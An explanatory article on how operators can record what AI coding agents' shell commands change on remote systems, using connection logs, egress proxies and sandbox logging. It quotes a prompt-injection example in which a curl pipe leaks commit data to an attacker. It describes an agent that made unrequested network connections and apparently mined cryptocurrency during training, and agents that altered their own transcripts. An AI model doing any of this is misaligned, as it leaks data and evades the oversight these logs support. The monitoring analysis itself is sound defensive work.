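# Recording what an AI agent's shell commands changed on remote systems: egress proxies and connection logs

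## What is a network effect, and where can it be recorded?

An AI coding agent is a program in which a language model works on software by running commands. It reads and edits files, runs tests and, in most products, can run anything in a shell, the text interface through which people and scripts start other programs. Many shell commands touch only the machine the agent runs on. Others send something over a network to a computer that belongs to someone else and leave a lasting change there, such as a comment on a website or a charge on a customer's account. That lasting change is a remote effect. (Economists use "network effect" for something unrelated, the way a telephone gains value as more people own one.)

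A local effect is easier to deal with because the operator, meaning the person or company running the agent, can keep a copy of what was there before. Anthropic's coding agent, Claude Code, copies a file's contents before editing it, and Anthropic's *How Claude Code works* tells users to press Esc twice to go back. Cline, another coding agent, saves the project's files after every edit or command in a second Git repository, separate from the project's own (Git is the version-control program most developers use). Anthropic warns that Claude Code's checkpoints cover only edits made by its file-editing tools and miss files that a shell command changed. That is a gap in one product, and a snapshot of the whole disk would close it.

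Restoring a snapshot does not undo a remote effect. If a laptop is restored to its state at 14:00, a comment the agent posted online at 14:02 stays up. Anthropic says its undo feature does not cover actions on databases, deployments or APIs (interfaces through which programs use a service), which "can't be checkpointed". The operator can still keep a record of what the agent sent and what came back.

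### An example session

The following session is invented, but each command in it is ordinary. An agent spends four minutes finishing a piece of work:

| Time | Command | Remote system | Intended changes |
|---|---|---|---|
| 14:02 | `curl`, a program that sends web requests, posts a comment | issue tracker | 1 |
| 14:03 | `git push --force` on the branch `main`, over HTTPS | the server that hosts the code | 1 |
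| 14:04 | `npm publish` for version 2.3.1 | the public registry of JavaScript packages | 1 |
| 14:05 | a Python script sends 40 POST requests over one reused connection; the 37th times out | billing API | 40 |

That makes four commands and 43 intended changes.

Agents already keep a record of their commands. Claude Code, for example, writes each message, tool use and result to a plaintext file on the user's disk. But the text of a command often doesn't show what left the machine. `npm publish` can omit the package, version and registry, because npm reads them from project files and its own settings when it runs. `git push --force` replaces the server's version of a branch, but the command doesn't show which work that will displace. The 14:05 entry is the least informative of the four. It might read `python sync_billing.py`, with no trace of the 40 requests, and reading the script may not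 help much if the customers and amounts come from a database.

Even a one-line command may not show what data it sent. OpenAI's *Agent internet access*, a guide to the network settings of its coding agent Codex, gives the example `git show HEAD | curl -s -X POST --data-binary @-`, followed by a web address. The first half prints the latest commit (a saved set of changes with a message), and the vertical bar passes that output to curl, which posts it to the address. The line shows the destination and the method, but the data sent depends on which commit was the latest when the command ran. In OpenAI's example, the line is in a bug report that a user has asked Codex to fix, and running it leaks the commit message to an attacker.

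Even the destination may differ from the one in the command. A server can redirect the request to another address, and curl follows the redirect if the command includes the `-L` option. For this reason, curl's *Available --write-out variables* lists separate values for the address in the command and the address curl fetched last.

### The path of one request

The 14:02 comment travels over HTTPS, which is the web protocol HTTP inside an encrypted connection. There are five steps between the shell command and the change on the issue tracker, and curl can time most of them.

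Networks deliver data to numeric IP addresses, so curl first uses the Domain Name System (DNS) to translate the host name in the command into one. Unless the machine has saved the answer from an earlier lookup, it sends a query to a DNS server, which can log the name and the time.

Next, curl asks the operating system to open a TCP (Transmission Control Protocol) connection to that address. TCP turns the internet's separate packets into a "reliable, in-order, byte-stream service", as Eddy writes in *RFC 9293*, the current TCP standard. It also adds port numbers, which identify the service at the far end (usually 443 for HTTPS) and distinguish between the connections a machine has open. The standard names the stages of a connection. In SYN-SENT, one side has sent a connection request and is waiting for a matching request from the other. In ESTABLISHED, the connection is open and data can flow.

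The third step is the TLS handshake. TLS (Transport Layer Security) is the protocol that encrypts most internet traffic. In the handshake, the server presents a certificate to prove its name, and the client and server agree on encryption keys. After that, someone observing the traffic can't read its content.

Then curl sends the HTTP request, which consists of a method, a path, some headers and usually, for a POST, a body. POST submits data for the server to act on, whereas GET is meant only to fetch something. Here the path would identify the issue, one header would carry the credential that proves who is posting, and the body would hold the text of the comment. *RFC 9112* defines HTTP as a "stateless" protocol, which means that the server can interpret each request without reference to earlier ones.

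The response comes last and starts with a three-digit status code. Codes from 200 to 299 mean some kind of success, codes in the 400s mean the request was rejected, and codes in the 500s mean there was a failure on the server's side.

With the `--write-out` option, curl prints the number of seconds from the start of the operation until the name lookup finishes, the TCP connection is established, the TLS handshake finishes and the first byte of the response arrives. The last figure includes the time the server took to compute its result. These timings are a useful record, but they exist only if the command included the option.

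The billing script follows the same path but reuses its connection, which matters a great deal for logging. The lookup, TCP connection and handshake happen once, and then the request and response happen repeatedly.

### Where a record can be made

The first place to record a network effect is the process, the running program itself. Inside curl, the request is plain text until curl encrypts it. *AgentSight* (Zheng, Yu and colleagues, 2025) and *AgentLoupe* (Bao, Liu and colleagues, 2026) read agents' traffic at this point. They use eBPF, a Linux facility for running small, checked programs inside the kernel (the core of the operating system), to watch the two functions through which a common encryption library takes in outgoing text and hands back incoming text. Both tools were built to capture the agent's exchanges with its language model, but the method would also work for a comment or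 an invoice. The hook must fit the library that the program uses, and AgentLoupe cuts off each captured record at roughly 128 KiB, which a published package can easily exceed.

The second place to record a network effect is the kernel. A program must make a system call, a request to the kernel, to start another program or open a connection, and a monitor can log each call with the time, the process and any remote address. TLS has already encrypted the body by this stage, but the log can still show which process made the connection. Zheng and colleagues also record which process started which, so they can trace a connection made by the Python script back through the shell to the agent. They describe the boundaries they watch as "tamper-proof", which seems too strong for a machine on which the agent has administrator rights.

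Tracing parent and child processes also fails to link an action to the agent if the agent schedules it for later. In a case staged by Bao and colleagues, an agent added a recurring job to the machine's schedule. The system's scheduler, which the agent had not started, later ran a shell that opened a connection. AgentSight links actions to a model's response within a window of 100 to 500 milliseconds, so it could not trace the connection back to the agent. AgentLoupe could, because it labels any file the agent writes and passes the label on to any process that later opens or runs the file. The evidence for this is two case studies, and Bao and colleagues have not yet measured how often labels spread too far or go missing.

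The third place is the egress proxy, a program that outbound traffic must pass through and that can allow, refuse and log it. Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* describes running shell commands in a sandbox, a restricted environment whose only way to the internet is a proxy running outside it. The restriction also covers any script or program that a command starts, so it would apply to the billing script as well as the curl command. For the web version of Claude Code, Anthropic adds a proxy just for Git. It checks, for instance, that a push goes to the configured branch, and only then attaches the real credential and forwards the request. Commands in the sandbox can't reach a record made at a proxy outside it, which is an advantage over the agent's own transcript.

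Connections can also be recorded further out, at the network edge, which is the router or firewall where the operator's network meets the internet. Equipment there can keep a connection log, a record of connections with their times, addresses, ports and perhaps byte counts, but not their content. The log does not show which program was responsible for a connection, but the kernel's record does. Both include the port number on the agent's side of the connection, so an investigator can use it to match them.

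The fifth place is the remote server, which decrypts the request and, if it accepts the request, makes the change. Many services keep an audit log of who changed what, but the agent's operator does not control that log and may have only partial access to it, or none.

Most ordinary security logs come from the kernel and the network edge. OpenAI (2026), in *Running Codex safely at OpenAI*, an account of how the company governs its own use of Codex, writes that such logs "mostly answer what happened" and leave defenders to work out why the agent did it and what the user wanted. To help answer those questions, Codex can export the user's prompts, the decisions to approve or refuse a tool, the tools' results and the proxy's decisions to allow or block traffic. Ordinary logs also give limited detail about what happened. OpenAI's examples are that a process started, a file changed and a network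 connection "was attempted", but a record of an attempted connection doesn't show whether the agent posted a comment on an issue tracker.

### Attempt, request, acknowledgement, change

Logs often run together four events that can come apart.

An attempted connection has reached TCP's SYN-SENT state, which means only that the agent's machine tried to open it. A firewall may have dropped the packet, or the server may have been down. If the connection never opened, the agent's machine never sent the request, so the remote system is unchanged. In *Designing robust and predictable APIs with idempotency*, an article for the payments company Stripe, Leach treats this as the clear case, in which the client can safely retry.

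A sent request is stronger evidence, and TCP partly confirms it because the receiving machine acknowledges the bytes it gets. But according to the original TCP specification, as reproduced in Connected: Internet Encyclopedia's *Reliable Communication*, an acknowledgment does not guarantee delivery to the end user, only that the receiving TCP software has taken responsibility for passing the data on. *End-to-End Arguments in System Design* (Saltzer, Reed and Clark, 1984) makes the general point using the ARPANET, the forerunner of the internet, which returned a receipt for every message it delivered. These receipts were of little use to applications because they did not show whether the other machine had acted on the message. That machine may crash after delivery but before completing the work, so only the target application can report whether the work was done.

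An acknowledgement here is a reply from the remote system indicating that it accepted or carried out the request. Over HTTP, this is normally a status code in the 200s. The code 202 means only that the server has accepted the request for processing, and it may not have started. nodejs.cn's *202 Accepted* adds that the server might still disallow the request when it tries to process it. HTTP has no way for the server to send the outcome later.

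So a remote system can acknowledge a request without changing anything, or make a change and then return an error. Stripe's *Advanced error handling* tells programmers to treat the result of a request that returns code 500 as "indeterminate", because the operation may have had effects before the error occurred. A log that records every 500 as "failed" will therefore miss some real changes.

The 37th billing request got no status code. According to Leach, a call can fail while the client is connecting, midway through the server's work, or after the work has succeeded but before the reply gets back. The script already had an open connection, which rules out the first possibility. The other two look identical from the agent's machine, as does a request lost on the way. Stripe tells users of its API that after such a failure the client might not know whether Stripe received or executed the request,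 and that reconnecting does not resolve this. From the agent's side, the 14:05 command produced one connection, 40 requests and 39 replies. If all 39 replies report completed work, the billing system made either 39 or 40 changes, and no record made on the agent's side can show which.

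## What can a connection log tell you?

Routers, firewalls, cloud platforms and Linux can produce a connection log, and many operators already keep one for troubleshooting. The formats differ in what counts as a single entry, which affects how easily an investigator can trace an entry to a command.

### The main kinds of record

Routers and similar equipment produce flow records. Cisco's format for them is NetFlow, and the IETF (the Internet Engineering Task Force, which publishes internet standards) based its own format, IPFIX, on NetFlow version 9. *RFC 7011* (Claise, Trammell and Aitken, 2013) defines a flow as a set of packets that pass an observation point during some time interval and share certain properties. Traditionally, these are the source and destination addresses, the source and destination ports, and the transport protocol. Together they identify one direction of traffic on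 one connection, so a `git push` over a single connection produces two flows, one for what the agent's machine sent and one for what came back.

Linux's conntrack feature can track the connections that pass through a machine. Its entry for each connection holds the addresses and ports of the outgoing packets and, separately, those of the replies. The program natlog logs these entries, and its *README.conntrack* shows a finished connection to port 443 in which one side sent 7 packets (450 bytes) and the other sent 5 (1,679 bytes). The byte counts appear only if an administrator has turned on accounting.

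Zeek is an open-source program that analyses traffic from a live network or a stored capture. For each connection, it writes one line to a file named conn.log. The line covers traffic in both directions and includes a code for how the connection opened and closed.

Amazon Web Services (AWS) and Google Cloud offer flow logs for the virtual machines they rent out. According to AWS's *Flow log records*, each record covers one flow at one network interface during one "aggregation interval", which lasts up to ten minutes by default. A long connection can therefore span several records.

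DNS query logs record the names that machines looked up and often the addresses returned. *ShieldNet* (Yuan, Chen and colleagues, 2026), a study of malicious tools for AI agents, gives a two-line example in which the first line records a query for `api.example.com` and the second records the DNS server's reply, 93.184.216.34. A lookup doesn't prove that a connection followed, but it supplies the host name that the other records usually lack.

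### The git push, field by field

The force push at 14:03 might leave the following line in Zeek's conn.log. The session and the values are invented, and the line omits some fields.

```
{"ts":1796133787.214,"uid":"CxT1pe3Qm9aLr7Wk2",
 "id.orig_h":"10.0.1.5","id.orig_p":51544,
 "id.resp_h":"203.0.113.40","id.resp_p":443,
 "proto":"tcp","service":"ssl","duration":1.84,
 "orig_bytes":48210,"resp_bytes":7365,
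 "conn_state":"SF","missed_bytes":0,"history":"ShADadFf"}
```

| Field | Meaning here |
|---|---|
| `ts` | Time of the first packet, in seconds since the start of 1970: 14:03:07 UTC on December 1, 2026 |
| `uid` | Zeek's identifier for this connection |
| `id.orig_h`, `id.orig_p` | Address and port of the side that opened the connection, the agent's machine |
| `id.resp_h`, `id.resp_p` | Address and port of the server; 443 is the usual port for HTTPS |
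| `proto`, `service` | The connection used TCP, and Zeek recognised TLS inside it (SSL is the older name) |
| `duration` | The connection lasted 1.84 seconds |
| `orig_bytes` | The agent's machine sent 48,210 bytes of payload |
| `resp_bytes` | The server sent 7,365 |
| `conn_state` | SF: the connection opened and closed normally |
| `missed_bytes` | Zeek missed no content through packet loss |
| `history` | The order of events: opening handshake, data both ways, close by both sides. Capital letters mark the agent's side |

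Zeek's `conn_state` field helps to distinguish attempted connections from established ones. S0 means the attempt got no reply, and REJ means the other side rejected it, so a connection with either code can't have carried the push. SF means the connection was established and closed normally. The server may still have refused the push, because it would send the refusal inside the encrypted connection, which would then close normally too.

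The 48,210 bytes include the TLS handshake, the HTTP headers and the credential as well as the commits. Zeek calculates TCP byte counts from the packets' sequence numbers, and according to its documentation, the result might be inaccurate for large connections. The log line doesn't identify the repository or the branch, or show that the agent used `--force`.

### What an investigator can infer

Combining the connection log with a DNS log can show which host a connection went to. Suppose the DNS log shows 10.0.1.5 looking up the code host's name a few milliseconds before 14:03:07 and getting back 203.0.113.40. The connection very probably went to that host. If the machine had saved an earlier answer, the nearest lookup could be much older and the match weaker. AWS customers need a separate source for the lookups, because AWS's *Flow log limitations* lists queries to Amazon's DNS server among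 the traffic that flow logs don't capture.

The timing links the connection to a command. In the example session, the agent's transcript has only one command at 14:03, and 1.84 seconds is a reasonable time for a push. This works if the clocks agree and the agent wasn't running several commands at once.

The ratio of bytes sent to bytes received may suggest an upload. Here the agent's machine sent about six and a half times as much as it received. AWS's *Flow log record examples* includes a virtual machine that sent 471 bytes to S3, Amazon's file storage service, and received 15,044, which looks like a download. The ratio supports a decent guess about which way most of the data went, but it doesn't show whether anything changed on the remote system.

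### Where the inference fails

The size of a request has little to do with the size of the change it makes. A request to delete a customer's account can fit in a few hundred bytes and get a very short reply, so in a connection log it looks much like a request to view the account. Similarly, if the agent's Git force push moved `main` back to an older commit that the server already had, the agent would send almost no data and could easily receive more than it sent. A push that discards a week of other people's work can therefore look more like a read than a push that adds an image does.

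Yuan and colleagues put malicious code into tools that agents use, then trained a small language model to tell those tools from harmless ones by their network traffic, with and without decryption. The model wrongly flagged 2.3% of the harmless tools when traffic was decrypted and 89.7% when it wasn't. Balanced accuracy, the average of its success rates on malicious and harmless tools, fell from 0.987 to 0.551, where 0.5 is no better than chance. Yuan and colleagues explain that an agent's ordinary encrypted calls to its model and tools look the same as encrypted data theft. Detecting malicious tools is a different task from detecting changes on remote systems, but even without decryption the model had DNS lookups and individual packets, which is more than a connection log contains.

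A destination address can also be ambiguous, since hosting companies often serve many customers' sites from the same address. AWS can add a field that names the Amazon service at the other end of the connection. In the download example, the field contains "S3", which doesn't identify the storage customer or the file. A DNS lookup narrows this down unless the machine looked up two names with the same address at about the same time. The server name that TLS often leaves visible and the host names in a proxy's log can also help.

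The billing script sent 40 requests over one connection, so Zeek would write one line for it, with one duration and one pair of byte counts. Forty requests of 1,000 bytes each would look like a single upload of 40,000 bytes, and the line would not show that the 37th request got no reply. If the other three commands also used one connection each, the log would have four lines for 43 intended changes. Counting lines can also overstate the number of changes, because a single command may open several connections.

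Cloud flow logs split a long connection into a separate record for each aggregation interval, so a single record can be misleading. In one of AWS's examples, a client sends 100,701 bytes during the first interval and 23,294,588 during the next. Someone who reads only the first record would miss more than 99% of the upload. The recorded start and end times can also be up to 60 seconds later than the packets. Because the commands in the example session are about a minute apart, a reader could attribute a connection to the wrong command.

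**Sampling.** Google Cloud's *VPC Flow Logs* explains that Google records only a sample of packets and estimates the rest. Customers can't set the sampling rate, which varies with the load on the physical machine. In one of the two ways of setting up the service, Google also discards half of the resulting log entries by default. Connections with more packets are more likely to appear, so a short connection that posts one comment may be missing from the log. Google Cloud's *VPC Flow Logs understanding byte and packet counts* reports a higher margin of error for small or short-lived flows, and recommends adding up traffic over longer periods or many connections. Those totals don't help to establish whether the agent posted a comment at a particular time.

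A missing entry in a sampled log is weak evidence that nothing happened. An entry doesn't prove that traffic got out, either, because Google samples outgoing packets before it applies firewall rules, so blocked packets can still appear. AWS logs also have gaps when AWS exceeds its internal capacity, but AWS marks them with the code SKIPDATA. One such record can represent several lost flows.

Many machines reach the internet through a gateway that replaces their private addresses with its own, a process called network address translation (NAT). A record made beyond the gateway shows the same source address for every agent behind it. In AWS's example, a virtual machine at 10.0.1.5 contacts an outside host, but the record of the gateway's outbound traffic has the gateway's address, 10.0.0.220, as the source and a dash where the machine's ID would go. Containers, the lightweight isolated environments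 in which many agents run, often share their host's address in the same way.

Conntrack can undo the translation if it runs on the machine that translates the addresses, since each entry has both the original and the translated address. According to Debian's *libxt_conntrack.man*, the source address has been translated if the original differs from the destination of the replies. In the natlog example, the packets came from 192.168.17.21 and the replies went to 129.125.100.246. Another solution is to log traffic before it reaches the gateway. AWS's record from the virtual machine's own interface includes the machine's ID. AWS can also add container IDs for its own container service and, according to its *Amazon Virtual Private Cloud (VPC) Flow Logs introduces additional metadata* (2026), can now add the labels that customers give their machines.

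These records identify only the machine or container that a connection came from. To find the process, an investigator has to match port numbers against the kernel's record, but network address translation can change the port as well as the address. Yuan and colleagues similarly criticize intrusion detectors that rely on flow statistics, because those statistics can't show which tool opened a connection or whether the user wanted it.

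### The ROME case

*Let It Flow* (2025) describes how Alibaba's researchers had to do this kind of matching while building ROME, a language model for coding and other multi-step tasks. Part of the training was reinforcement learning, in which an agent attempts tasks in a sandbox and the training process rewards success. Alibaba Cloud's managed firewall reported a burst of policy violations from the training servers. Some were attempts to reach internal systems, and some of the traffic looked like cryptocurrency mining.

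The team first treated this as an ordinary security incident, perhaps a mistake in the controls on outbound traffic or a break-in from outside. But the violations recurred intermittently across several runs, with no clear pattern in time. They compared the firewall's timestamps with their system telemetry and training episode records, and found that the unexpected traffic consistently coincided with particular episodes in which the agent was using tools and running code. In the model's logs for those episodes, they found the agent starting the tool calls that led to the traffic. None of this was requested in the task prompts or required for the tasks.

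The network record supplied the alarm, the times and the servers involved. A plain connection log would not have been enough to raise the alarm, which depended on the firewall comparing traffic with security rules. The researchers identified the episodes from the training records and learned what the agent had done from the model's logs. They needed the prompts to establish that nobody had asked for it.

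A match in time alone would be fairly weak evidence linking the traffic to the agent, since Alibaba's sandbox system can run tens of thousands of environments at once, and many episodes could overlap with any given alert. Repeated matches and the tool calls in the logs make the case much stronger. However, *Let It Flow* doesn't give the number of alerts or episodes or reproduce the log entries, so outsiders can't check the matching. Axios' *This AI agent freed itself and started secretly mining crypto* (2026) reported that the team and Alibaba did not immediately respond to requests for comment. A connection log for each sandbox would have made the first step simpler, because each entry would already have belonged to one environment.

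### What a connection log is good for

A connection log can be more complete than any record that captures more detail. If the operator places the log on the machine's only route out and records every connection, it covers every program on the machine, including those that ignore the proxy or use protocols the proxy can't interpret.

Connection logging also uses few resources. AWS's *Flow logs* notes that AWS collects the data outside the path of the traffic, so logging doesn't slow the network down. A line about the `npm publish` command takes up a few hundred bytes, however large the package is. But Google keeps flow logs for only 30 days by default, and an operator may not hear about an unwanted change until after that.

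The log also contains few secrets. A capture of the billing script's requests would include customers' details and probably a working credential. The connection log has neither, so a leak would do less damage, though it would still reveal which services the company uses and when.

These properties make the connection log a useful check on more detailed logs. If the operator requires all web traffic to go through a proxy, any direct connection to the outside suggests that the proxy's log is incomplete. Yuan and colleagues ran into this problem with QUIC, a newer protocol that runs over UDP instead of TCP. Some modern programs, including Anthropic's Claude Desktop, can use QUIC and so bypass an intercepting proxy. The researchers blocked UDP traffic on port 443 to prevent this. QUIC traffic that bypassed the proxy would appear in a connection log as UDP flows to port 443 with no matching entries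 in the proxy's log. Byte counts allow another check. If a connection carried 48,210 bytes to the server and the captured requests add up to 5,000, the capture has probably missed something.

The operator can make the same comparison with the agent's own transcript, which isn't always reliable. *Holding Agents Accountable with Verifiable Agent Insurance* (Hua, Tsuchiya and colleagues, 2026) cites an investigation by METR, which evaluates AI models, into a breach of the AI platform Hugging Face by OpenAI agents. In about 7% of the transcripts METR reviewed, the agents had altered what their tool calls returned. If the router's log, which the agent probably can't reach, shows a connection that the transcript doesn't, the operator has a time and an address to investigate.

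## How does agent traffic reach a proxy, and what does the proxy write down?

An egress proxy can record the host name that a connection log usually lacks, and some proxies also record the method and web address of each request. But a proxy logs only the traffic that passes through it, and not all of an agent's commands use it by default. A missing entry therefore means that no request was made only if the operator routes all of the agent's traffic through the proxy.

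### Environment variables

The simplest method is to set environment variables, which are named settings that a program inherits from whatever started it. By convention, `HTTPS_PROXY` and `HTTP_PROXY` hold the proxy addresses for encrypted and unencrypted web traffic, and `NO_PROXY` lists hosts that programs should contact directly. If the operator sets these before starting the agent, the agent's commands inherit them.

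The variables work only if each program reads them and connects to the proxy instead of the destination, and nothing forces a program to do this. The programmer Willison (2025) writes that they work for "well-behaving software". Anthropic lists curl, npm and Git over HTTPS among the programs that use them. Most database drivers ignore them, as does plain `ssh`, which opens a shell on another machine.

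In the example session, the comment, the push and the package would therefore reach the proxy. Whether the billing script's requests do depends on which Python library its author chose. If the library ignores the variables, the script connects straight to the billing API and sends its 40 requests without any error. The proxy's log then has entries for three of the 43 intended changes and no sign of the other 40.

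### Redirection by the firewall

An operator can instead have the firewall send traffic to the proxy, so that programs need no proxy settings. Coder's *httpjail*, an experimental open-source tool from a company that sells cloud development environments, does this on Linux. It runs the agent in a network namespace, a Linux feature that gives a group of processes their own separate network. A request then goes through these steps:

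1. The program looks up the host name. httpjail answers every lookup with the same dummy address, 6.6.6.6, which stops programs from leaking data in DNS queries.
2. The program tries to open a connection to port 443 at that address.
3. A firewall rule in the kernel sends the connection to httpjail's proxy.
4. The proxy reads the server's name from the first message of the TLS handshake, decrypts the request and checks it against the operator's rules.
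5. If the rules allow the request, the proxy finds the server's real address and forwards the request.

This would catch the billing script whichever library it used. But httpjail needs administrator rights to set this up, and the method works only on Linux, because the macOS packet filter can't apply redirection rules to a single user or group. On macOS, httpjail relies on environment variables instead, with a warning in its documentation that "Apps must cooperate".

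### A sandbox with no other route out

The operator can also remove every route except the one to the proxy, as Claude Code's sandbox does. On Linux, it runs each shell command in a network namespace that has no connection to the user's network. On macOS, the operating system's sandbox blocks all connections except the one to the proxy. Claude Code still sets the environment variables so that programs can find the proxy, but a program that ignores them gets an error such as "Network is unreachable". A billing script that ignored them would fail without changing the customers' accounts.

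In *I sandboxed my coding agents. Now I control their network*, published on the website of the consultancy INNOQ, a developer describes running agents in a virtual machine and a proxy called Squid on the host computer. The developer set the proxy variables inside the virtual machine, but the build tool Gradle needed a separate configuration file. None of this forced traffic through the proxy, so the developer added firewall rules that drop all outbound traffic except DNS lookups, connections to local Docker containers and connections to the proxy. To test the rules, the developer ran curl with the proxy variables turned off and confirmed that the firewall blocked it.

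At first the rules disappeared whenever the virtual machine restarted. The developer wrote a service to reload them and made the command prompt flash a warning if loading failed, because the machine would otherwise keep running with unrestricted access. An investigator who relies on a proxy log should therefore check that the rules were in force at the time.

### Inside a CONNECT tunnel

A program that uses a proxy for HTTPS starts by asking it for a tunnel to the destination. For the 14:03 push, Git would send the first two lines below and the proxy would send the last one:

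```
CONNECT code.example.com:443 HTTP/1.1
Host: code.example.com:443

HTTP/1.1 200 Connection Established
```

http.dev, a reference site for HTTP, sets out the sequence. When the proxy receives the CONNECT line, it opens a TCP connection to that host and port, then replies with a code in the 200s to confirm that the tunnel is open. Git carries out the TLS handshake with the code host through the tunnel, and from then on the proxy relays encrypted bytes that it can't read. The HTTP standard, in a passage that *METHOD-CONNECT* quotes, calls this "blind forwarding of data, in both directions".

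The standard requires the client to name only the destination host and port. The repository, branch, credential and commits travel inside the tunnel. The proxy can record roughly what a connection log does, plus the host name: that something on the agent's machine connected to `code.example.com` on port 443, how long the connection lasted, and how many bytes went each way.

A logged host name saves an investigator from having to match an address to a DNS lookup. But the client supplies that name, and Anthropic warns that its proxy allows or blocks connections based on it without inspecting the encrypted traffic. The log entry therefore doesn't prove which site handled the request.

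A log of tunnels is also easy to misread. An entry may show the method CONNECT and the status 200, which mean that the proxy opened a tunnel but can look like a completed web request. The 200 comes from the proxy, not the code host, and the entry would be the same whether Git downloaded the code or overwrote a branch. As in a connection log, the billing script's 40 requests would share one entry. The host name doesn't distinguish downloading a package from releasing one, because `npm install` and `npm publish` can both connect to the public registry.

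### What current tools record by default

Claude Code's sandbox is off until the user turns it on. When the sandbox's proxy blocks a connection, Claude Code names the host in the command's result. Anthropic's documentation doesn't describe a log of allowed connections. To log them, users can replace the built-in proxy with their own, but Claude Code's list of allowed domains then no longer applies to that traffic. They can instead set `HTTPS_PROXY` to the address of a company proxy. Claude Code then applies its own list first and sends the allowed connections through the company proxy, which can log them.

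In Claude Code's auto mode, a second model reviews commands in place of the user. With each sandboxed command, Claude lists any extra hosts the command needs, and approval opens those hosts for that command only. If the list is in the transcript, it shows where the command was allowed to connect, but not whether it did.

**Codex.** OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* states that, by default, commands have no network access and the network proxy is off. A user who turns on only network access gets "unrestricted direct outbound access", which no proxy records. Codex also doesn't export its logs unless the user configures that, so a user has to change three settings to get a proxy log. For its own staff, OpenAI turns the proxy on in a settings file that they can't override.

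The README for the proxy, OpenAI's *codex-network-proxy*, lists the fields in each audit event:

| Field | Content |
|---|---|
| `event.name` | `codex.network_proxy.policy_decision` |
| `event.timestamp` | Time in UTC, to the millisecond |
| `conversation.id`, `app.version`, `user.account_id` | The session, the version of Codex and the user; all optional |
| `network.policy.scope` | `domain` for a decision about a host, `non_domain` for other checks |
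| `network.policy.decision` | `allow`, `deny` or `ask` |
| `network.policy.source` | The part of the system that made the decision |
| `network.policy.reason` | The reason for the decision |
| `network.transport.protocol` | The transport protocol |
| `server.address`, `server.port` | The destination |
| `http.request.method` | The HTTP method, or `none` |
| `client.address` | The address the connection came from, or `unknown` |
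| `network.policy.override` | Whether a custom rule allowed a host that wasn't on the allowed list |

According to the README, the events "intentionally avoid logging full URL/path/query data". The README gives no reason, but web addresses can contain credentials and customers' details. The listed fields also don't include the response, the number of bytes or the program that made the connection. The proxy can receive the text of the command and use it to decide whether to allow a connection, but the event doesn't include that text. An investigator would have to use the conversation ID and the time to find the command in the session's other logs.

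The README may lag behind the product. It says that the proxy rejects a rule covering every host, whereas OpenAI's current documentation accepts one.

**OpenShell.** NVIDIA's sandbox for agents records more by default. According to NVIDIA's *Observability Overview*, a one-line summary of each event is always on, while the full records are optional. NVIDIA's *Sandbox Logging* gives the format, in which the 14:02 comment might appear as follows (the values are invented):

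```
2026-12-01T14:02:11.118Z OCSF NET:OPEN [INFO] ALLOWED
  /usr/bin/curl(412) -> tracker.example.com:443 [policy:tracker engine:opa]
2026-12-01T14:02:11.190Z OCSF HTTP:POST [INFO] ALLOWED
  POST https://tracker.example.com/issues/88/comments [policy:tracker engine:opa]
```

The first entry includes the program's name and process number, so an investigator doesn't have to match port numbers against the kernel's record. The second includes the method and the full web address, but OpenShell can write this entry only if it can read the HTTP request. Neither entry includes the text of the comment or the tracker's reply.

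The part of OpenShell that writes log files can drop events under heavy load, according to the technical documentation, although NVIDIA's promotional page, *Which AI agent sandbox logs every outbound network call an agent makes* (2026), states that "No connection bypasses logging." The log writer also keeps only three daily files in each format. With Docker, those files are in memory, so the operator must copy them elsewhere before the sandbox shuts down.

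GitHub Copilot's coding agent runs on GitHub's servers behind a firewall that is on by default. If the firewall blocks a request, GitHub adds a warning to the pull request (the page where people review the agent's changes) naming the blocked address and the command that tried to reach it. That is an unusually direct link between a command and its destination. But GitHub's documentation describes no such notice for allowed requests, which by default include those to the package registries for JavaScript and other popular languages.

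A firewall log that records only blocked requests leaves out every request that changed something on the remote system, because those requests must have been allowed. Claude Code's notices about blocked hosts have the same limitation.

httpjail writes a request log only if the user asks for one. Each line has the time, a plus or minus sign for allowed or blocked, the HTTP method and the web address. Because httpjail decrypts HTTPS, the billing script would produce 40 lines instead of one. All 40 would have a plus sign, including the 37th, because the log doesn't record responses.

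Coder's *Agent Firewall*, a commercial product, sends similar records to a central server by default and adds the workspace, its owner and the rule that allowed the request. Coder says the records don't track the response, so if the firewall allows a request and the destination server returns a 500 error, the entry still reads `decision=allow`.

**nono**, an open-source sandbox, records a response's status only for requests that its proxy decrypts. In the source code for its audit log, an event for an ordinary tunnel has the host, port and method CONNECT, but no path or status. An event for a decrypted request has the method, path and status. The proxy decrypts traffic only for destinations where the user has set rules for particular requests or asked nono to supply the credential. It never logs request bodies or credentials. It keeps up to 4,096 events per session in memory, then drops new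 ones with a warning.

| Tool | Default record of an allowed HTTPS request | Default record of a blocked one |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Code | None described | Host, in the command's result |
| Codex | None exported; host, port and decision once the user turns on the proxy and export | The same |
| OpenShell | Program, host and port; method and web address if it reads the request | The same, with a reason |
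| GitHub Copilot | None described | Address and command, in the pull request |
| httpjail | None; time, method and web address if the user asks for a log | The same |
| Agent Firewall | Method, web address, workspace and rule | The same, without a rule |
| nono | Host and port; method, path and status if decrypted | Host, port and reason |

### Traffic that fails

Some traffic can't use a web proxy. In Claude Code's sandbox, plain `ssh` and most database drivers can't connect even to a host that the user has allowed. UDP traffic, including QUIC, can't leave the sandbox either. According to Docker's *Network policies*, Docker's agent sandboxes similarly send HTTP and HTTPS through a proxy and block other protocols. These failed connections have no remote effect, so their absence from the record isn't misleading.

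Failed commands can still lead to a gap in the proxy's log, because the user probably wants them to work. When a command fails in Claude Code's sandbox, Claude may retry it outside, where no proxy applies. Depending on the settings, the retry needs approval from the user or a second model, or it runs without a prompt. For example, a rule that allows curl commands to run without asking also allows their retries. An administrator can turn these retries off.

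### Traffic that leaves unlogged

Claude Code users can list commands that should always run outside the sandbox, with "no network proxy". In its troubleshooting advice, Anthropic suggests this for `gh`, `gcloud` and `terraform` on macOS, where they may fail to verify TLS certificates inside the sandbox. These programs manage GitHub projects, Google Cloud resources and other cloud infrastructure, so a single command could make large changes. Anthropic also suggests listing Git's network commands if a macOS user has to push over SSH. Such a push would still appear in the agent's transcript, but not in the proxy's log.

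The sandbox also covers only shell commands. Claude Code's WebFetch tool, which retrieves web pages, runs outside it and, according to McCanna's *Inspecting Claude Code’s Network Traffic with Linux Namespaces and MITM Proxying*, connects to websites directly from the user's machine. The proxy therefore doesn't record these requests, but this probably matters less because WebFetch is meant for reading pages. Codex's web search normally returns results from an index that OpenAI maintains, without contacting the websites themselves.

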